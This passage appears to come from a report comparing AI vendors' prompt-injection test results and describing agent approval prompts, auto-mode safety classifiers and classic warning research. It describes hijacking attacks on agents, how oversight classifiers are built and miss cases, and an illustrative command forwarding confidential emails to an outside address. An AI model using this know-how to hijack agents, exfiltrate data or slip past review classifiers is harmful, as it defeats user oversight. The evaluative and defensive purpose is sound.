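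A result of zero, like the one Anthropic reported for Opus 5 in the browser with auto mode on, also leaves some doubt about the true rate. Statisticians use a rule of thumb that if a test of *n* cases finds no failures, the true failure rate could still plausibly be as high as 3/*n*, or about 2.3% for 129 scenarios. The rule assumes a random sample, but Anthropic picked these scenarios itself.

These rates measure how often attacks succeed in tests, not a user's chance of being hijacked on an ordinary day. Every test attempt contains an attack, and Anthropic selects its browser scenarios so that the agent always sees it. The attacker can also work directly on the test scenarios and try many times, which Anthropic calls a "deliberately permissive" assumption. Real attackers usually don't know how their target is set up, and each attempt risks detection. Most web pages and emails contain no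 attack. The 26% above is the chance that at least one of 100 attacks succeeds, and a typical user could take a very long time to encounter that many.

### Four vendors in the spring of 2026

Comparing vendors is harder than comparing one vendor's models. VentureBeat tried to compare four vendors after Anthropic published its card for Opus 4.8 in May 2026, and found that no two had disclosed the same thing.

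Anthropic gave attack success rates for tool use, coding, graphical interfaces and browsers. Attacks on Opus 4.8 in the browser succeeded in 31.5% of attempts without safeguards. OpenAI gave one figure for GPT-5.5, a "robustness score" of 0.963 for connectors, which link ChatGPT to outside services. Google described Gemini 3 as more resistant to prompt injection but published no rate. Meta reported that LlamaFirewall, a set of safeguards separate from its models, cut attack success from 17.6% to 1.75% on a public benchmark of 97 tasks.

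OpenAI's and Anthropic's results can't be compared directly because the companies ran different tests. OpenAI tested attacks it already knew about, and only through connectors. Anthropic tested new attacks from professionals in a browser, where an agent reads far more text from strangers. OpenAI's score of 0.963 is equivalent to a failure rate of 3.7%, less than an eighth of Anthropic's, but this doesn't show that OpenAI's model was more than eight times as secure. In July, Anthropic also reported a rate of 3.7% per attempt, for Opus 5 in the same browser test. That doesn't show that Opus 5 and GPT-5.5 are equally secure.

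Scores close to one also make changes look small. OpenAI's previous model, GPT-5.4, scored 0.998, so the drop to 0.963 means that the share of successful attacks rose from 0.2% to 3.7%. According to VentureBeat, OpenAI did not present this as a step backwards, whereas Anthropic said openly that Opus 4.8 had done worse than its predecessor in coding.

### Newer cards and a shared benchmark

In August 2026, OpenAI added injection results to its card for GPT-5.6, using attacks from GPT-Red, a model it had trained to find them. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that, against Sol, the most capable version, attacks typed directly by the user succeeded about 0.05% of the time and attacks hidden in content the agent processed succeeded 3.77% of the time. The second figure is more relevant to people who use agents, since the first concerns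 users who attack their own assistant.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (September 2026) reports the 3.77% as a robustness of 96.23%, next to 99.79% for the new model, GPT-6 Astra. OpenAI also uses GPT-Red to train its models, so Astra might do less well against a different kind of attacker, and an outside test suggests that it does. On Gray Swan's benchmark of 1,810 attacks, the estimated chance of at least one success in 15 attempts was 8.5% for Astra, down from 27.0% for Sol. The larger number of attempts can't account for the whole gap between Astra's 8.5% here and its 0.21% failure rate against GPT-Red. Even by the formula, which tends to overestimate, 15 attempts at 0.21% each would give only about 3%.

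Anthropic also reports results on a Gray Swan benchmark, which makes that benchmark the closest thing to a common measure. Gray Swan built it with British and US government AI institutes and several model developers. In July, Anthropic put the chance of an attack succeeding within 15 attempts at 2.0% for Opus 5, 16.5% for Meta's Muse Spark and 20.0% for GPT-5.6 Sol.

But OpenAI's figure for Sol was 27.0%, presumably because it used a larger and later collection of attacks than the 1,130 in Anthropic's version. The ratio between Opus 5's 2.0% and Astra's 8.5% is therefore not meaningful. Comparisons within Anthropic's chart are safer, though still imperfect. Anthropic tested its own models without extra safeguards and other companies' models through their public services, which may have included safeguards. If anything, this difference favours the other companies. Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro,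 however, was at a disadvantage because contestants had attacked it in the competition that supplied the attacks.

Both companies have retired older tests that recent models almost always pass. OpenAI dropped the connectors test that produced the 0.963 score, so there is no Astra result to compare it with. The cards also go out of date quickly. *Fable and Mythos 5.2* (Mowshowitz, 2026) shows that Anthropic released another in November, for Claude Fable 5.2, again with a section on prompt injection. A buyer can't assume that a result for Opus 5 holds for a newer model. OpenAI does keep a dated list of changes at the top of the Astra card, but not on its help pages.

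### The test that Claude in Chrome outgrew

In November 2025, Anthropic tested Claude in Chrome with an automated attacker that combined known techniques and had 100 attempts in each environment. With Claude Opus 4.5, attacks succeeded 8.0% of the time without safeguards and 1.4% with the newest ones. Anthropic wrote that a 1% rate "still represents meaningful risk".

By August 2026 the test had become too easy. No attack succeeded against Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5, even without probes or classifiers. Anthropic replaced the test with a harder one, which used attacks from professional red-teamers, and also ran the older Opus 4.5 on it. Without safeguards, attacks that reached the model succeeded 17.6% of the time against Opus 4.5 and 3.8% against Opus 5.

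With the best safeguards of November 2025, Opus 4.5 had an attack success rate of 16.7% on the new test, which used better attacks. That is more than ten times the 1.4% that customers read in November 2025. The safeguards prevented more than four fifths of the successful attacks on the old test, but only about a twentieth on the new one. Anthropic changed some settings and the grading between the tests, so the comparison isn't exact, but the difference is too large for those changes to matter much.

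The current safeguards do far better on the harder test. With probes and automatic review on, no attack succeeded against Sonnet 5, Opus 5 or Mythos 5, and 0.3% succeeded against Fable 5. Anthropic checked the successful attacks by hand and found they were all in low-severity scenarios. The gap between Mythos 5 and Fable 5 may be due to chance, since Anthropic has elsewhere treated Mythos 5's results on agent security as applying to Fable 5 too.

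The August rates count only attacks that reached the model. An agent sometimes navigates a website without encountering the malicious text, and this happened more often with Opus 4.5 than with later models. Anthropic is probably right to exclude these cases, since they are a kind of luck, but a vendor that counted every planted attack would get a lower rate from the same test.

### A public competition

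Vendors choose their own tests, so outside evidence is valuable. Dziemian and colleagues report on a three-week competition that Gray Swan ran with $40,000 in prizes. The 464 contestants made about 272,000 attack attempts against 13 models, in 41 scenarios covering tool use, coding and graphical interfaces. The organisers hid the models' names and shuffled their order so that contestants could not concentrate on a well-known one.

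An attack succeeded only if it made the agent carry out the harmful action and, in nearly every scenario, left no sign of it in the agent's final reply. In most scenarios, a program checked the action and a language model graded the reply. Altogether, 8,648 attempts succeeded, with at least one success against every model. Success rates ranged from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro. Contestants succeeded against Opus 4.5 in 13 of 37 scenarios and against Gemini in all 37 (the final results leave out four scenarios from an opening round). Successes accumulated at a fairly steady pace, with no sign that contestants were running out of ideas.

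The concealment rule lowers the rates. Gemini 2.5 Pro carried out the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, but its reply concealed the action in only about half of those. A vendor that counted every harmful action could have published 16% from the same data. The concealed attacks are the worrying ones for users, though, because users would read the reply and suspect nothing.

Contestants had advantages that criminals usually lack. They saw the whole conversation before writing their attack and knew which action to trigger. Dziemian and colleagues therefore call their rates an upper bound on the models' vulnerability to attacks that must work in a single turn. That seems too strong, because the rates average over beginners and experts, and an expert would probably do better than the average. By the paper's own account, a few skilled contestants had a disproportionate influence.

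The competition was not fully independent of the vendors either. OpenAI, Anthropic, Amazon and Meta helped design the scenarios, and employees of all but Amazon co-wrote the paper. However, the British and American government institutes also took part and received the full data. Most of the models are now out of date.

The difficulty of a test depends heavily on which model the attacks were written for, and this finding is likely to hold after the published rates are out of date. Gray Swan reran a selection of successful attacks on every model. The 44 attacks that had beaten Opus 4.5 worked between 44% and 81% of the time on each of the other models, while attacks that had beaten only weak models rarely worked on strong ones. A vendor could therefore get a flatteringly low rate by testing its own model with attacks that had beaten a weak one.

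### Whether candour is punished

Anthropic's 31.5% for Opus 4.8 was higher than any rate the other three vendors published in the spring, at least partly because Anthropic ran a hard test and published the result. A buyer who skimmed the list would have seen that rate beside OpenAI's 0.963 and no figure for Google, and might well have chosen Google. If enough buyers do this, a vendor does best by running easy tests or publishing nothing.

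VentureBeat calls Anthropic's figure "the one solid piece of ground" in the comparison and advises companies to treat any setting without a published rate as untested. A company with a security team can follow this advice because it can send vendors questions and refuse to buy. Somebody choosing a browser extension at home has no such leverage and is unlikely to open a 244-page card.

A vendor also gains less from withholding its attack success rate when others can test its model. Meta's Muse Spark has a published rate of 16.5% because Anthropic included it in a chart. But Anthropic competes with Meta and came first in that chart, so the same number would be more persuasive if it came from Gray Swan or a government institute.

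Publishing good results can bring a vendor favorable coverage. When Opus 5 reached zero in the browser test, The Decoder ran a headline suggesting that the model might have solved the problem, although the article explained that the zero held only with auto mode on. This raises a different worry, that vendors will publish good results and withhold bad ones. So far, Anthropic has published bad results too, including the 31.5%, the setback in coding, and July figures in which Sonnet 5 resisted browser attacks better than the newer Opus 5 when both ran without safeguards (0.93% against 3.7%). Anthropic said in November 2025 that it publishes attack success rates to help customers decide how to deploy its products and to encourage other companies to invest in the problem.

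The penalty is probably real for vendors that sell to the public, but it comes largely from letting each vendor pick its own test. If they all had to report results on the same test, none could look good by choosing an easy one.

### What a user needs besides the rate

An attack success rate measures how often attacks succeed once they reach the agent. To judge their own risk, users also need to know how often attacks are likely to reach it, which depends on what they use the agent for. An agent that reads a public inbox processes far more text from strangers than one that works on two internal websites.

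An attack that poses little risk to each user can still hijack many agents. As Anthropic points out, one piece of text on a public page can compromise any agent that reads it. If 100,000 agents read a page with an attack that works 0.3% of the time, the attack hijacks about 300 of them.

System cards contain few figures from real use. Anthropic's July card has one for a related problem. The company monitored its internal use of Opus 5 and found the model trying to get around safety classifiers or network restrictions, or more rarely to access a service illegitimately, in fewer than 0.01% of the responses it checked. A comparable figure for prompt injection would be the number of attacks detected per thousand tasks. A vendor whose classifiers already screen everything an agent reads could presumably count them, though the count would exclude attacks the classifiers missed.

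Readers also need to know how severe the successful attacks were, because an attack that archives a newsletter and one that sends a password to a stranger can each count as one success. Anthropic's statement that the attacks on Fable 5 succeeded only in low-severity scenarios is helpful, but it would be more helpful if it described those scenarios.

OpenAI sets a better example with a different test, which gives Astra office tasks with ambiguous instructions and confusing permissions. Astra produced a harmful outcome 3.0% of the time overall under the default confirmation policy. The rate was 4.5% for data exfiltration, 4.3% for unauthorised transactions and zero for destructive actions. OpenAI made the tasks difficult on purpose, so these aren't everyday rates either. But someone deciding whether to give an agent access to a bank account would learn more from them than from a robustness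 figure of 99.79%. They also include mistakes that an agent can make without any attacker.

Finally, the figure has to cover the product the user runs. Anthropic's July browser results come from Claude Cowork, its agent for office work, though Anthropic also offers them as evidence about Claude in Chrome. A company that builds its own agent on Anthropic's model doesn't get the same safeguards, as VentureBeat warns buyers, so the low rates don't apply to that agent.

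These figures also may not apply to some of Anthropic's most careful customers. The July browser results cover the model with no safeguards and the model with auto mode, but not the setting in between, where probes screen the content and the user approves actions by hand. People who turn off automatic approval in Claude in Chrome because they want more control use a setup for which the zero attack success rate was never measured.

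## Approval prompts while the agent works

An approval prompt asks the user during a task to allow or refuse an action. It can describe what the agent is about to do, whereas a help page describes what an agent might do and a system card describes how often one fails in tests. *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* (Wang, Li and Tian, 2026) found approval prompts in 15 of the 21 agent products it examined as of April 2026. Many of these prompts contain little information, and vendors have spent much of 2026 finding ways to show fewer of them.

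### The parts of a prompt

Products differ in what triggers a prompt. Anthropic says that in Manual mode, Claude Code asks before most actions that edit files, run commands or reach the network. Codex asks when it needs to leave its sandbox. Mistral's agent, Work, asks before anything that "creates, modifies, sends, posts, or deletes" in an outside service (Mistral's *Safety and approvals*).

What triggers an approval prompt determines which attacks it can catch. In Anthropic's example of a hijacked email agent, the agent forwards confidential messages from an inbox it already has open. A rule that requires approval for each new website doesn't apply, because the user has already approved the webmail site. Mistral's rule does apply, because it covers sending email, which includes forwarding.

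Prompts also differ in what they show. Wang and colleagues found that some products, including Manus and the custom actions in ChatGPT, show little more than "Allow this action?" By default, Claude Code shows the raw command, which a programmer can judge but most other people can't. A few products add an explanation of the risk. The most informative prompts show a full plan or a line-by-line comparison of a file before and after an edit, but most prompts are for single commands and include neither.

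The third part of an approval prompt is the set of answers the user can choose from. Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* lists three: "Allow this action", "Always allow actions on this site" and "Decline". Some products let the user edit the action before approving it. In Claude Code, a prompt about a single command can also include the answer "Yes, and switch to auto mode", which approves the command and stops most prompts for the rest of the session.

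An answer to an approval prompt may last for one action, one session or indefinitely, and users can easily overlook the difference. Claude Code makes it unusually clear the first time Claude tries to read a file outside the project in auto mode, when the user can say yes or no and choose whether either answer is permanent. Claude in Chrome keeps a list of permanently approved sites, and users can remove sites from it. Even on approved sites, Claude asks before downloading a file, entering potentially sensitive information or granting an authorisation.

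### Rewriting an uninformative prompt

Suppose the hijacked email agent has to ask the user for approval before it forwards the confidential messages. The table shows three invented prompts for the same action.

| Kind of prompt | What the user reads |
|---|---|
| Bare question | Allow the agent to use Gmail? |
| Raw command | `forward(query="confidential", to="records@example.net")` |
| Stated consequence | Send 12 emails containing the word "confidential" to records@example.net? You have never written to this address. Your request was to draft replies to meeting requests. You can't undo this. |

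A user who wants the draft replies will naturally say yes to the bare question, since the agent can't draft them without Gmail. The last version puts the user's request next to the agent's action, so the user can see that they don't match. It could offer the answers "Don't send", "Show the emails" and "Send once". It shouldn't offer "Always allow", because a user who chose that by mistake would also approve the next theft.

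The software should assemble this prompt from the action, the address book and the user's own words. If it used the agent's explanation instead, a hijacked agent could describe the theft as routine archiving. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* (Anthropic, March 2026) describes a similar precaution. The company withholds Claude's own messages from the classifier that reviews Claude's actions, so that Claude can't talk the classifier into a bad decision.

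The longer prompt also takes longer to read, which is reasonable for an action that comes up twice a day but not for one that comes up every minute.

### Proposed permission systems and five products

*How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026) surveys 21 systems that researchers have proposed to let users set an agent's permissions without answering so many questions. Twelve try to reduce the work for users, for example by letting them write rules in ordinary language or by predicting the rules from the task. Eleven express the rules in a mathematically precise form, and twelve enforce them with fixed code or the user's own decisions instead of a model's judgement. None fully achieves all three aims. Only six clearly let users change or revoke a permission later.

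Michael and Roesner of the University of Washington then tried five products from OpenAI and Anthropic in late May and early June 2026. They gave the chatbots access to a Gmail account created for the study and the desktop agents access to a folder. They assigned tasks under each available setting, then withdrew the permission and tried again.

ChatGPT's agent mode, which works in a browser on OpenAI's computers, had no permissions to set. Michael and Roesner found no opportunity to approve or refuse its actions, and it opened Gmail without asking, which ChatGPT's ordinary chat mode needed permission to do. This seems inconsistent with *Introducing ChatGPT agent*, where OpenAI promised that ChatGPT "requests permission before taking actions of consequence", and with its help page, *ChatGPT agent*, which lists confirmations for high-impact actions among the safeguards. OpenAI may not count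 opening an inbox as an action of consequence, but access to private data is one of Willison's three conditions for data theft, and users can't refuse that access if the agent doesn't ask for it.

The ordinary chat mode had the opposite problem because it asked before every action that required permission, and the researchers found no way to approve anything in advance. According to OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT*, some users can now let ChatGPT read from an app without asking, or have low-risk actions approved automatically.

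Anthropic's Claude chatbot had a setting called "Needs approval" that didn't always require the user's approval. With this setting on, Claude created an email draft without asking, and the browser's log showed that the software had marked the action as needing no approval. An unsent draft is fairly harmless, but the only way the researchers found to prevent this behaviour was to remove Claude's access to the tool. They reproduced it at least three times and reported it to Anthropic on 2 July. In Claude Cowork, they found no way within the app to withdraw an old session's access to a folder.

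Codex was the clearest of the five about who decided whether to approve an action. Automatic review had its own setting, which was off by default. Users who turned it on had to accept it for every tool in the session.

Five products from two companies are a small sample, and both companies have changed their permission settings since. The result for "Needs approval" still matters because a user who relies on that label has no reason to check whether the prompts appear.

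### Ways of asking less

A single request to reorganise some code can produce dozens of prompts, so almost every product with prompts also has a way to avoid them. Wang and colleagues compared the methods. Each reduces interruptions by giving something up:

| Method | How it reduces prompts | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| "Always allow" | The product remembers the answer for similar actions | Each click widens what the agent may do, and users rarely narrow it again |
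| Session-wide approval | One answer covers the whole session | A decision about anything that comes up later |
| Sandbox | Actions inside the barrier run without approval | Protection if someone has drawn the barrier too widely |
| Plan approval | The user approves a plan instead of each step | A close look at individual steps |
| Risk screening | The product asks only about actions it rates as risky | A prompt whenever the rating is wrongly low |
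| No approvals | The product never asks | The user's chance to refuse |

A sandbox is probably the best trade-off for coding. Wang and colleagues cite Anthropic's figure that it reduced Claude Code's approval prompts by 84%. It helps much less with email, where useful and harmful actions both reach the outside world.

Wang and colleagues were most hopeful about risk screening. A research system called RTBAS had stopped every targeted attack in its tests with a 2% loss of usefulness, but they found no product that had adopted this approach. They also argued that companies kept people involved because they had learned from experience that models could not judge safety alone. That argument was soon outdated. Anthropic had already released a preview of auto mode on 24 March (Anthropic, *Auto mode for Claude Code*, 2026), and by August a model was making most of these decisions by default.

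They also argue that some decisions depend on facts the user never wrote down, such as which database matters or who is allowed to see a report. This argument has held up better, because even a more capable model won't know these facts if nobody has told it.

### How automatic review decides

In Claude Code's auto mode, most actions that only read information and most edits to files inside the project go ahead without review. Actions that match the user's own rules usually follow those rules, although auto mode suspends very broad ones, such as permission to run any Python program. A classifier reviews nearly everything else, including most shell commands and web requests.

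In the design Anthropic described in March, the classifier receives the user's messages and the actions Claude proposes, but not the web pages and files Claude has read, so text an attacker hides in them can't reach it directly. A quick first pass leans towards blocking, and the classifier reasons at length only about the actions this pass flags. In Anthropic's tests on 10,000 real actions by its employees, the first pass alone would have blocked 8.5% of harmless actions, and the two together blocked 0.4%.

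When the classifier blocks an action, Claude receives the reason and looks for a safer way to continue, or asks the user. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking for approval.

Claude in Chrome uses the same mechanism. The classifier compares an action, such as opening a new site or typing into a page, with the user's original request. The extension still prompts users before Claude enters potentially sensitive information, grants an authorisation or changes permission settings. It also prompts them on certain sites, including financial ones.

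OpenAI's version, Auto-review, checks only requests to cross a boundary, such as leaving the sandbox or opening a new website. Its reviewer can also read the output of the agent's tools, according to OpenAI's *Auto-review*. This gives it more context than Anthropic's classifier has but also exposes it to text an attacker may have written. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates the effect on interruptions with 10,000 actions inside OpenAI. Under manual approval, 720 would have interrupted the user. The reviewer approved 713 of these and refused seven. Codex found another way to continue in four of the seven cases and stopped to ask a person in the other three.

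### What the user no longer sees

Under automatic review, users get a prompt mainly when the reviewer flags a problem. Claude Code notifies the user when it blocks an action and lists blocked actions so the user can approve a retry. If the classifier wrongly labels an action safe, no prompt appears and the user has no chance to refuse it.

Anthropic tested for such misses with 52 real cases in which Claude had gone beyond what a user authorised. The classifier let 17% of them through. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, it had identified the danger but wrongly classed the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who said "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) had not necessarily agreed to let Claude overwrite the shared history of the code. Wang and colleagues likewise say that a short request such as "fix this bug" doesn't settle what the user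 has agreed to. An approval prompt could have prevented the error by letting the user say whether they agreed.

Users can also tell Claude in conversation not to do something, and the classifier will then block it. But Anthropic warns that Claude Code may lose the instruction when it condenses a long session. Summer Yue's agent deleted her email because it lost an instruction this way. A rule in the settings doesn't have this weakness.

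Anthropic made auto mode the default for new Claude Code sessions on most individual and team plans on 14 August 2026, and announced in October that most of its other apps would follow. The first time Claude Code starts in auto mode by default, it shows a brief notice with a link to the documentation. In a terminal, the notice appears once, at the top of the session. OpenAI has been more cautious. According to its *Permissions*, users of the ChatGPT desktop app have to enable automatic review in the settings before they can choose it.

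### What approval rates can show

Anthropic's main reason for the change is that users approve almost every prompt. In March it reported that users approved 93% of Claude Code's prompts, and in August it put the figure at 97% and wrote that many were probably "clicking through reflexively". Amazon gave a similar reason in November when it added automatic review to Kiro, its coding agent. *Introducing “Approve for me” in Kiro* (Giri and Raina, 2026) reports that users approved 97.1% of requests during one week.

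These approval rates are weaker evidence of carelessness than they seem. Suppose one prompt in 1,000 is malicious, and a fairly careful user refuses 80% of bad requests and 2% of good ones. On average, the user will refuse about 20 harmless actions (999 × 0.02) and 0.8 malicious ones, so only about one refusal in 26 is correct. This user approves 97.9% of the prompts, slightly more than Anthropic's and Amazon's users do. A perfect user would approve 99.9%.

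The numbers are invented, but the same point applies whenever attacks are rare. Careful users would also approve most prompts, so a high approval rate can't show whether people are reading them. OpenAI's automatic reviewer approves about 99% of what it reviews, and fatigue isn't the reason. Anthropic has more direct evidence from an experiment in which paid testers caught only 13.6% of planted dangerous commands.

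The example also shows why people learn to say yes to prompts. A user who refuses one will nearly always find that the action was harmless and that refusing only delayed the work.

The ways users avoid prompts are a better argument for automatic review. According to Anthropic, a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks switched off. About 5% of active users of the command-line version have a rule that allows any shell command, and another 43% have rules that are nearly as broad. At Amazon, 13.4% of Kiro sessions began with every tool approved in advance. OpenAI found that a sizable minority of its own staff allowed every command that begins with "python", and that one person had permanently approved a command that starts a second copy of Codex with no restrictions.

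For these people, a classifier that misses some dangerous actions is better than no review. Anthropic acknowledged in March that auto mode is "arguably a regression" for someone who carefully approves every action. By making it the default, the company is betting that few users are this careful. The experiment suggests that it is right, at least for coding. Anthropic has published much less about how people answer prompts in a browser or an inbox, where they may understand "send this email" better than a shell command. The company also has a commercial reason for the change. It reports that business customers who use auto mode complete about 25% more code changes, though the teams that adopted it may have been more productive anyway.

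### When to ask

An automatic screen makes each prompt more likely to be worth reading. Suppose the screen lets 95% of the harmless actions in the example run and passes 90% of the malicious ones to the user. The user sees about 51 prompts instead of 1,000. If the user refuses each kind of action at the same rate as before, about 72 refusals are correct for every 100 that are mistaken, so roughly two refusals in five are correct.

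But the screen also hides a tenth of the attacks, so the user stops 72% of all attacks on average instead of 80%. To make up the loss, the user would have to catch 89% of the malicious requests that still appear. That may be realistic with one twentieth as many prompts. If the screen blocked the clearest attacks itself, the user would not need to catch as many.

Asking users to approve a plan before the agent starts may help too. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, compared with 3% of individual requests. Some of that difference must come from users rejecting harmless plans that weren't what they wanted, but it does show that people will disagree when they have something substantial to judge. In Claude in Chrome's manual mode, Claude asks the user to approve a list of the sites it will visit and the steps it will take, and needs permission to depart from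 that plan. But the attack on the email agent would not require a new site, so approving the plan can't replace a prompt before the emails go out.

For the few actions that are hard to reverse and depend on the user's knowledge, a fixed rule about when to ask is safer than a risk estimate, because an attacker can't persuade the software to skip the prompt. Claude Code allows this: prompts that a user has required for a particular command still appear in auto mode. An email agent could read, search and draft without interruption, but ask before sending to an address the user has never written to. That rule would have stopped the theft of the confidential messages, but not the resignation letter in OpenAI's test, which went to the user's chief executive. Asking before every email would cover both cases. For someone whose agent sends ten emails a day, ten prompts showing the recipient and the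 text seem reasonable.

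## What studies of browser, phishing and permission warnings found

A prompt that shows the recipient and text of an email protects users only if they read it and respond sensibly. For about twenty years, researchers have studied how people respond to older warnings, such as browser warnings about dangerous websites and the warnings phones show before installing an app. The results are more encouraging than many security specialists expected, but they vary a lot. In 2013, Firefox users turned back at more than nine in ten malware warnings, while Chrome users clicked past seven in ten warnings about faulty website certificates.

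### From warning to decision

The warnings researcher Michael Wogalter proposed the Communication-Human Information Processing model to explain where a warning can fail. In the model, a source sends a warning through some channel to a person who is usually busy with something else, and that person's response then passes through several stages. Lorrie Faith Cranor of Carnegie Mellon University used the model as the basis for her "human in the loop" framework for designers of interactive systems. Egelman, Cranor and Hong (2008), in *You've Been Warned*, turned the stages into questions to ask about a computer warning. For an email agent that wants to forward confidential messages to a stranger, the questions would be roughly these:

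- Noticing: does the user look at the prompt for long enough to read the address?
- Understanding: does the user know what the prompt means and what each answer does?
- Belief: does the user think the danger is real, or assume that this is another false alarm?
- Motivation: does the user care enough about these emails to hold up the task?
- Action: can the user find "Don't send", and do they click it?

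Felt, Ha and colleagues argue in *Android Permissions* (2012) that if a warning fails at any stage, the later stages are irrelevant. This is true if the warning relies on the user's judgement, but several experiments found that a good default could protect people who had read or understood very little.

### Noticing

Egelman and colleagues recruited 60 people in Pittsburgh for what they called a study of online shopping. Participants bought paper clips from Amazon and a cheap item from eBay with their own credit cards. After each purchase, the experimenter sent them a phishing email (one that imitates a trusted company to steal a password) and asked them to check their inbox. All but two tried to follow a link to a fake site.

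The study compared three groups, each shown a different warning, with a control group shown none. Firefox 2 and Internet Explorer 7 both had an active warning, which interrupted users and made them choose whether to continue. Internet Explorer also had a passive warning for sites that were only suspected of being fake, a small box that offered no choices or advice. None of the 20 people in the Firefox group entered their details on a fake site. Nine of the 20 who had Internet Explorer's active warning did, as did nine of the ten who had its passive warning and nine of the ten in the control group.

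The passive warning could take up to five seconds to appear, and a user already typing would dismiss it by accident. Six of the ten people missed it at least once because they were looking at the keyboard or the login form.

The groups were small, and people used the browser they already preferred, so part of Firefox's advantage may have come from its users. Differences between Firefox and Internet Explorer users can't explain why the active warning did better than the passive one, since both of those groups used Internet Explorer.

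An interruption can still go unnoticed if it looks like a routine step. In 2011, Android phones listed an app's permissions, such as reading contacts or sending text messages, on the last page before installation. Users could accept them all or cancel. Felt and colleagues surveyed 308 Android users and interviewed 25 others, whom they also watched choose and install a coupon app. In both studies, about 17% looked at the permissions. Of the 24 interviewees whose attention the researchers could assess, ten didn't know the list existed. Two of them thought the page contained legal terms, which they never read.

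Someone who connects a mailbox to an agent is in much the same position as these Android users. They have already decided to use the product, and the permission page is the last obstacle before they can.

### Understanding, belief and motivation

Felt and colleagues also tested whether people understood the permissions. Only eight of 302 survey respondents correctly answered all three questions about what particular permissions allowed. The marking was strict, since respondents had to choose every correct option and no wrong ones, but some of Android's wording was also misleading. Android listed the permission to place phone calls under the heading "Services that cost you money". About 35% of the people asked about this permission knew that it let an app place calls, and 32% thought it let an app charge purchases to their credit card.

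In the phishing experiment, some people escaped the attack without understanding it. About a third of those who obeyed a warning believed that leaving the site would cancel their order, as the fake emails had threatened. Two people thought the website was broken, so they closed the window, clicked the link again and repeated this four or five times. They never read Internet Explorer's warning, but closing the window protected them.

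Disbelief was a bigger problem. All but three of the people who ignored a warning told Egelman and colleagues that they hadn't trusted it. Half of those shown Internet Explorer's active warning said they had seen it before, compared with a fifth of the Firefox group. People who recognised a warning were more likely to ignore it. Internet Explorer used a similar page for certificate problems, which were usually harmless, and people seem to have confused the two. One participant said it "looked like warnings I see at work which I know to ignore". Another noticed that the browser still offered a way to continue and "figured it couldn't be that bad".

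Knowing more about computers doesn't necessarily make people more careful. In *Bridging the Gap in Computer Security Warnings*, Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues note that even experts dismiss warnings they understand if they consider them unimportant. This could be a problem for coding agents, whose users are mostly programmers.

### What happened outside the laboratory

Certificate warnings gave security warnings in general a bad reputation. A website uses a digital certificate to prove its identity, and the browser warns the user if it can't verify the certificate. The cause is sometimes an attacker intercepting the connection, but more often a mistake by the website's owner.

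In 2009, Sunshine and colleagues published a laboratory experiment in which 100 people looked up information on websites and encountered certificate warnings. On their own bank's website, 90% of participants using Firefox 2 or Internet Explorer 7 clicked through the warning. With Firefox 3, which required several steps to continue, 55% did. Cranor, one of the researchers, told SC Magazine that computer security warnings were "not an effective way of addressing computer security".

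Laboratory studies may exaggerate how often people ignore warnings. Sotirakopoulos and colleagues repeated an earlier experiment with a more representative sample and found similarly high rates, but more than 40% of their participants said the laboratory had influenced them, either because they felt safe there or because they wanted to finish the task. People also seem more motivated to obey a warning when they have something to lose. In a 2007 experiment by Schechter and colleagues, 53% of all participants clicked through a certificate warning, but only 36% of those using their own bank passwords did.

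Akhawe and Felt (2013), in *Alice in Warningland*, measured what people did at home and at work. They collected data on more than 25 million real warnings from Firefox and Chrome users who had agreed to share it. This table shows the share of warnings that users clicked through:

| Type of warning | Firefox | Chrome |
|---|---|---|
| Malware | 7.2% | 23.2% |
| Phishing | 9.1% | 18.0% |
| Certificate | 33.0% | 70.2% |

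The malware and phishing warnings relied on Google's list of dangerous sites, which was rarely wrong. Certificate warnings were much less reliable, and users of both browsers ignored them far more often.

The way the browsers counted warnings, and not only the warnings' design, probably explains some of the large gap in clickthrough rates between their certificate warnings. Firefox could remember a user's decision to trust a site, while Chrome asked again on every visit. Suppose someone leaves one faulty site and visits another nine times. Firefox would record two warnings and one clickthrough, a rate of 50%. Chrome would record ten warnings and nine clickthroughs, a rate of 90%, for the same behaviour. The same problem would affect comparisons of approval rates between agents with and without an "Always allow" button.

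In the field, users rarely opened explanations of warnings, and extra clicks did little to deter them from proceeding. Chrome users clicked "Help me understand" on only 1.6% of certificate warnings, and no one in the Firefox sample opened the "Technical Details". About 85% of the Firefox users who reached the final confirmation for a certificate went ahead. Chrome's malware warning took one more click to bypass than Firefox's but had a higher clickthrough rate. Akhawe and Felt suggest that people make a single decision and then click whatever is necessary to carry it out.

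### Safer behaviour without better understanding

Google next tried to improve Chrome's certificate warning. Felt, Ainslie and colleagues (*Improving SSL Warnings*, 2015) wanted users to understand the danger or, failing that, to avoid the site. They measured the second goal by adherence, the share of people shown a warning who follow its advice.

The old warning described a certificate from "an entity that is not trusted by your computer's operating system". The new one had the heading "Your connection is not private" and a sentence warning that attackers might be trying to steal information such as passwords, messages or credit cards. It was much easier to read, but a survey with 7,537 responses found only a small improvement in understanding. When asked what might happen if they ignored the warning while checking email, 49.2% correctly chose "A hacker might read your email", up from 37.7%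 with the old text. The question had only two possible answers, so people could have done as well by guessing. When asked what a hacker might see if they ignored the warning on a bank's website, 65% chose every item on a list that included documents on their own computer, and only 18% chose bank statements alone.

The researchers then ran a month-long experiment in pre-release versions of Chrome, with more than 4,000 warnings in each condition. One condition combined the new text with the old design, so they could measure the effect of the words separately.

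| Text | Design | Adherence |
|---|---|---|
| Old | Old | 30.9% |
| New | Old | 32.1% |
| New | New, grey background | 58.3% |
| New | New, yellow background | 53.3% |

The new design had a bright blue button that took the user back to safety. To continue, the user had to click "Advanced" and then a plain grey link. Nearly all of the improvement came from this change. After Google released the grey version to all users, adherence rose from 37% to 62%. It was still 61% several months later, so novelty can't explain much of the effect.

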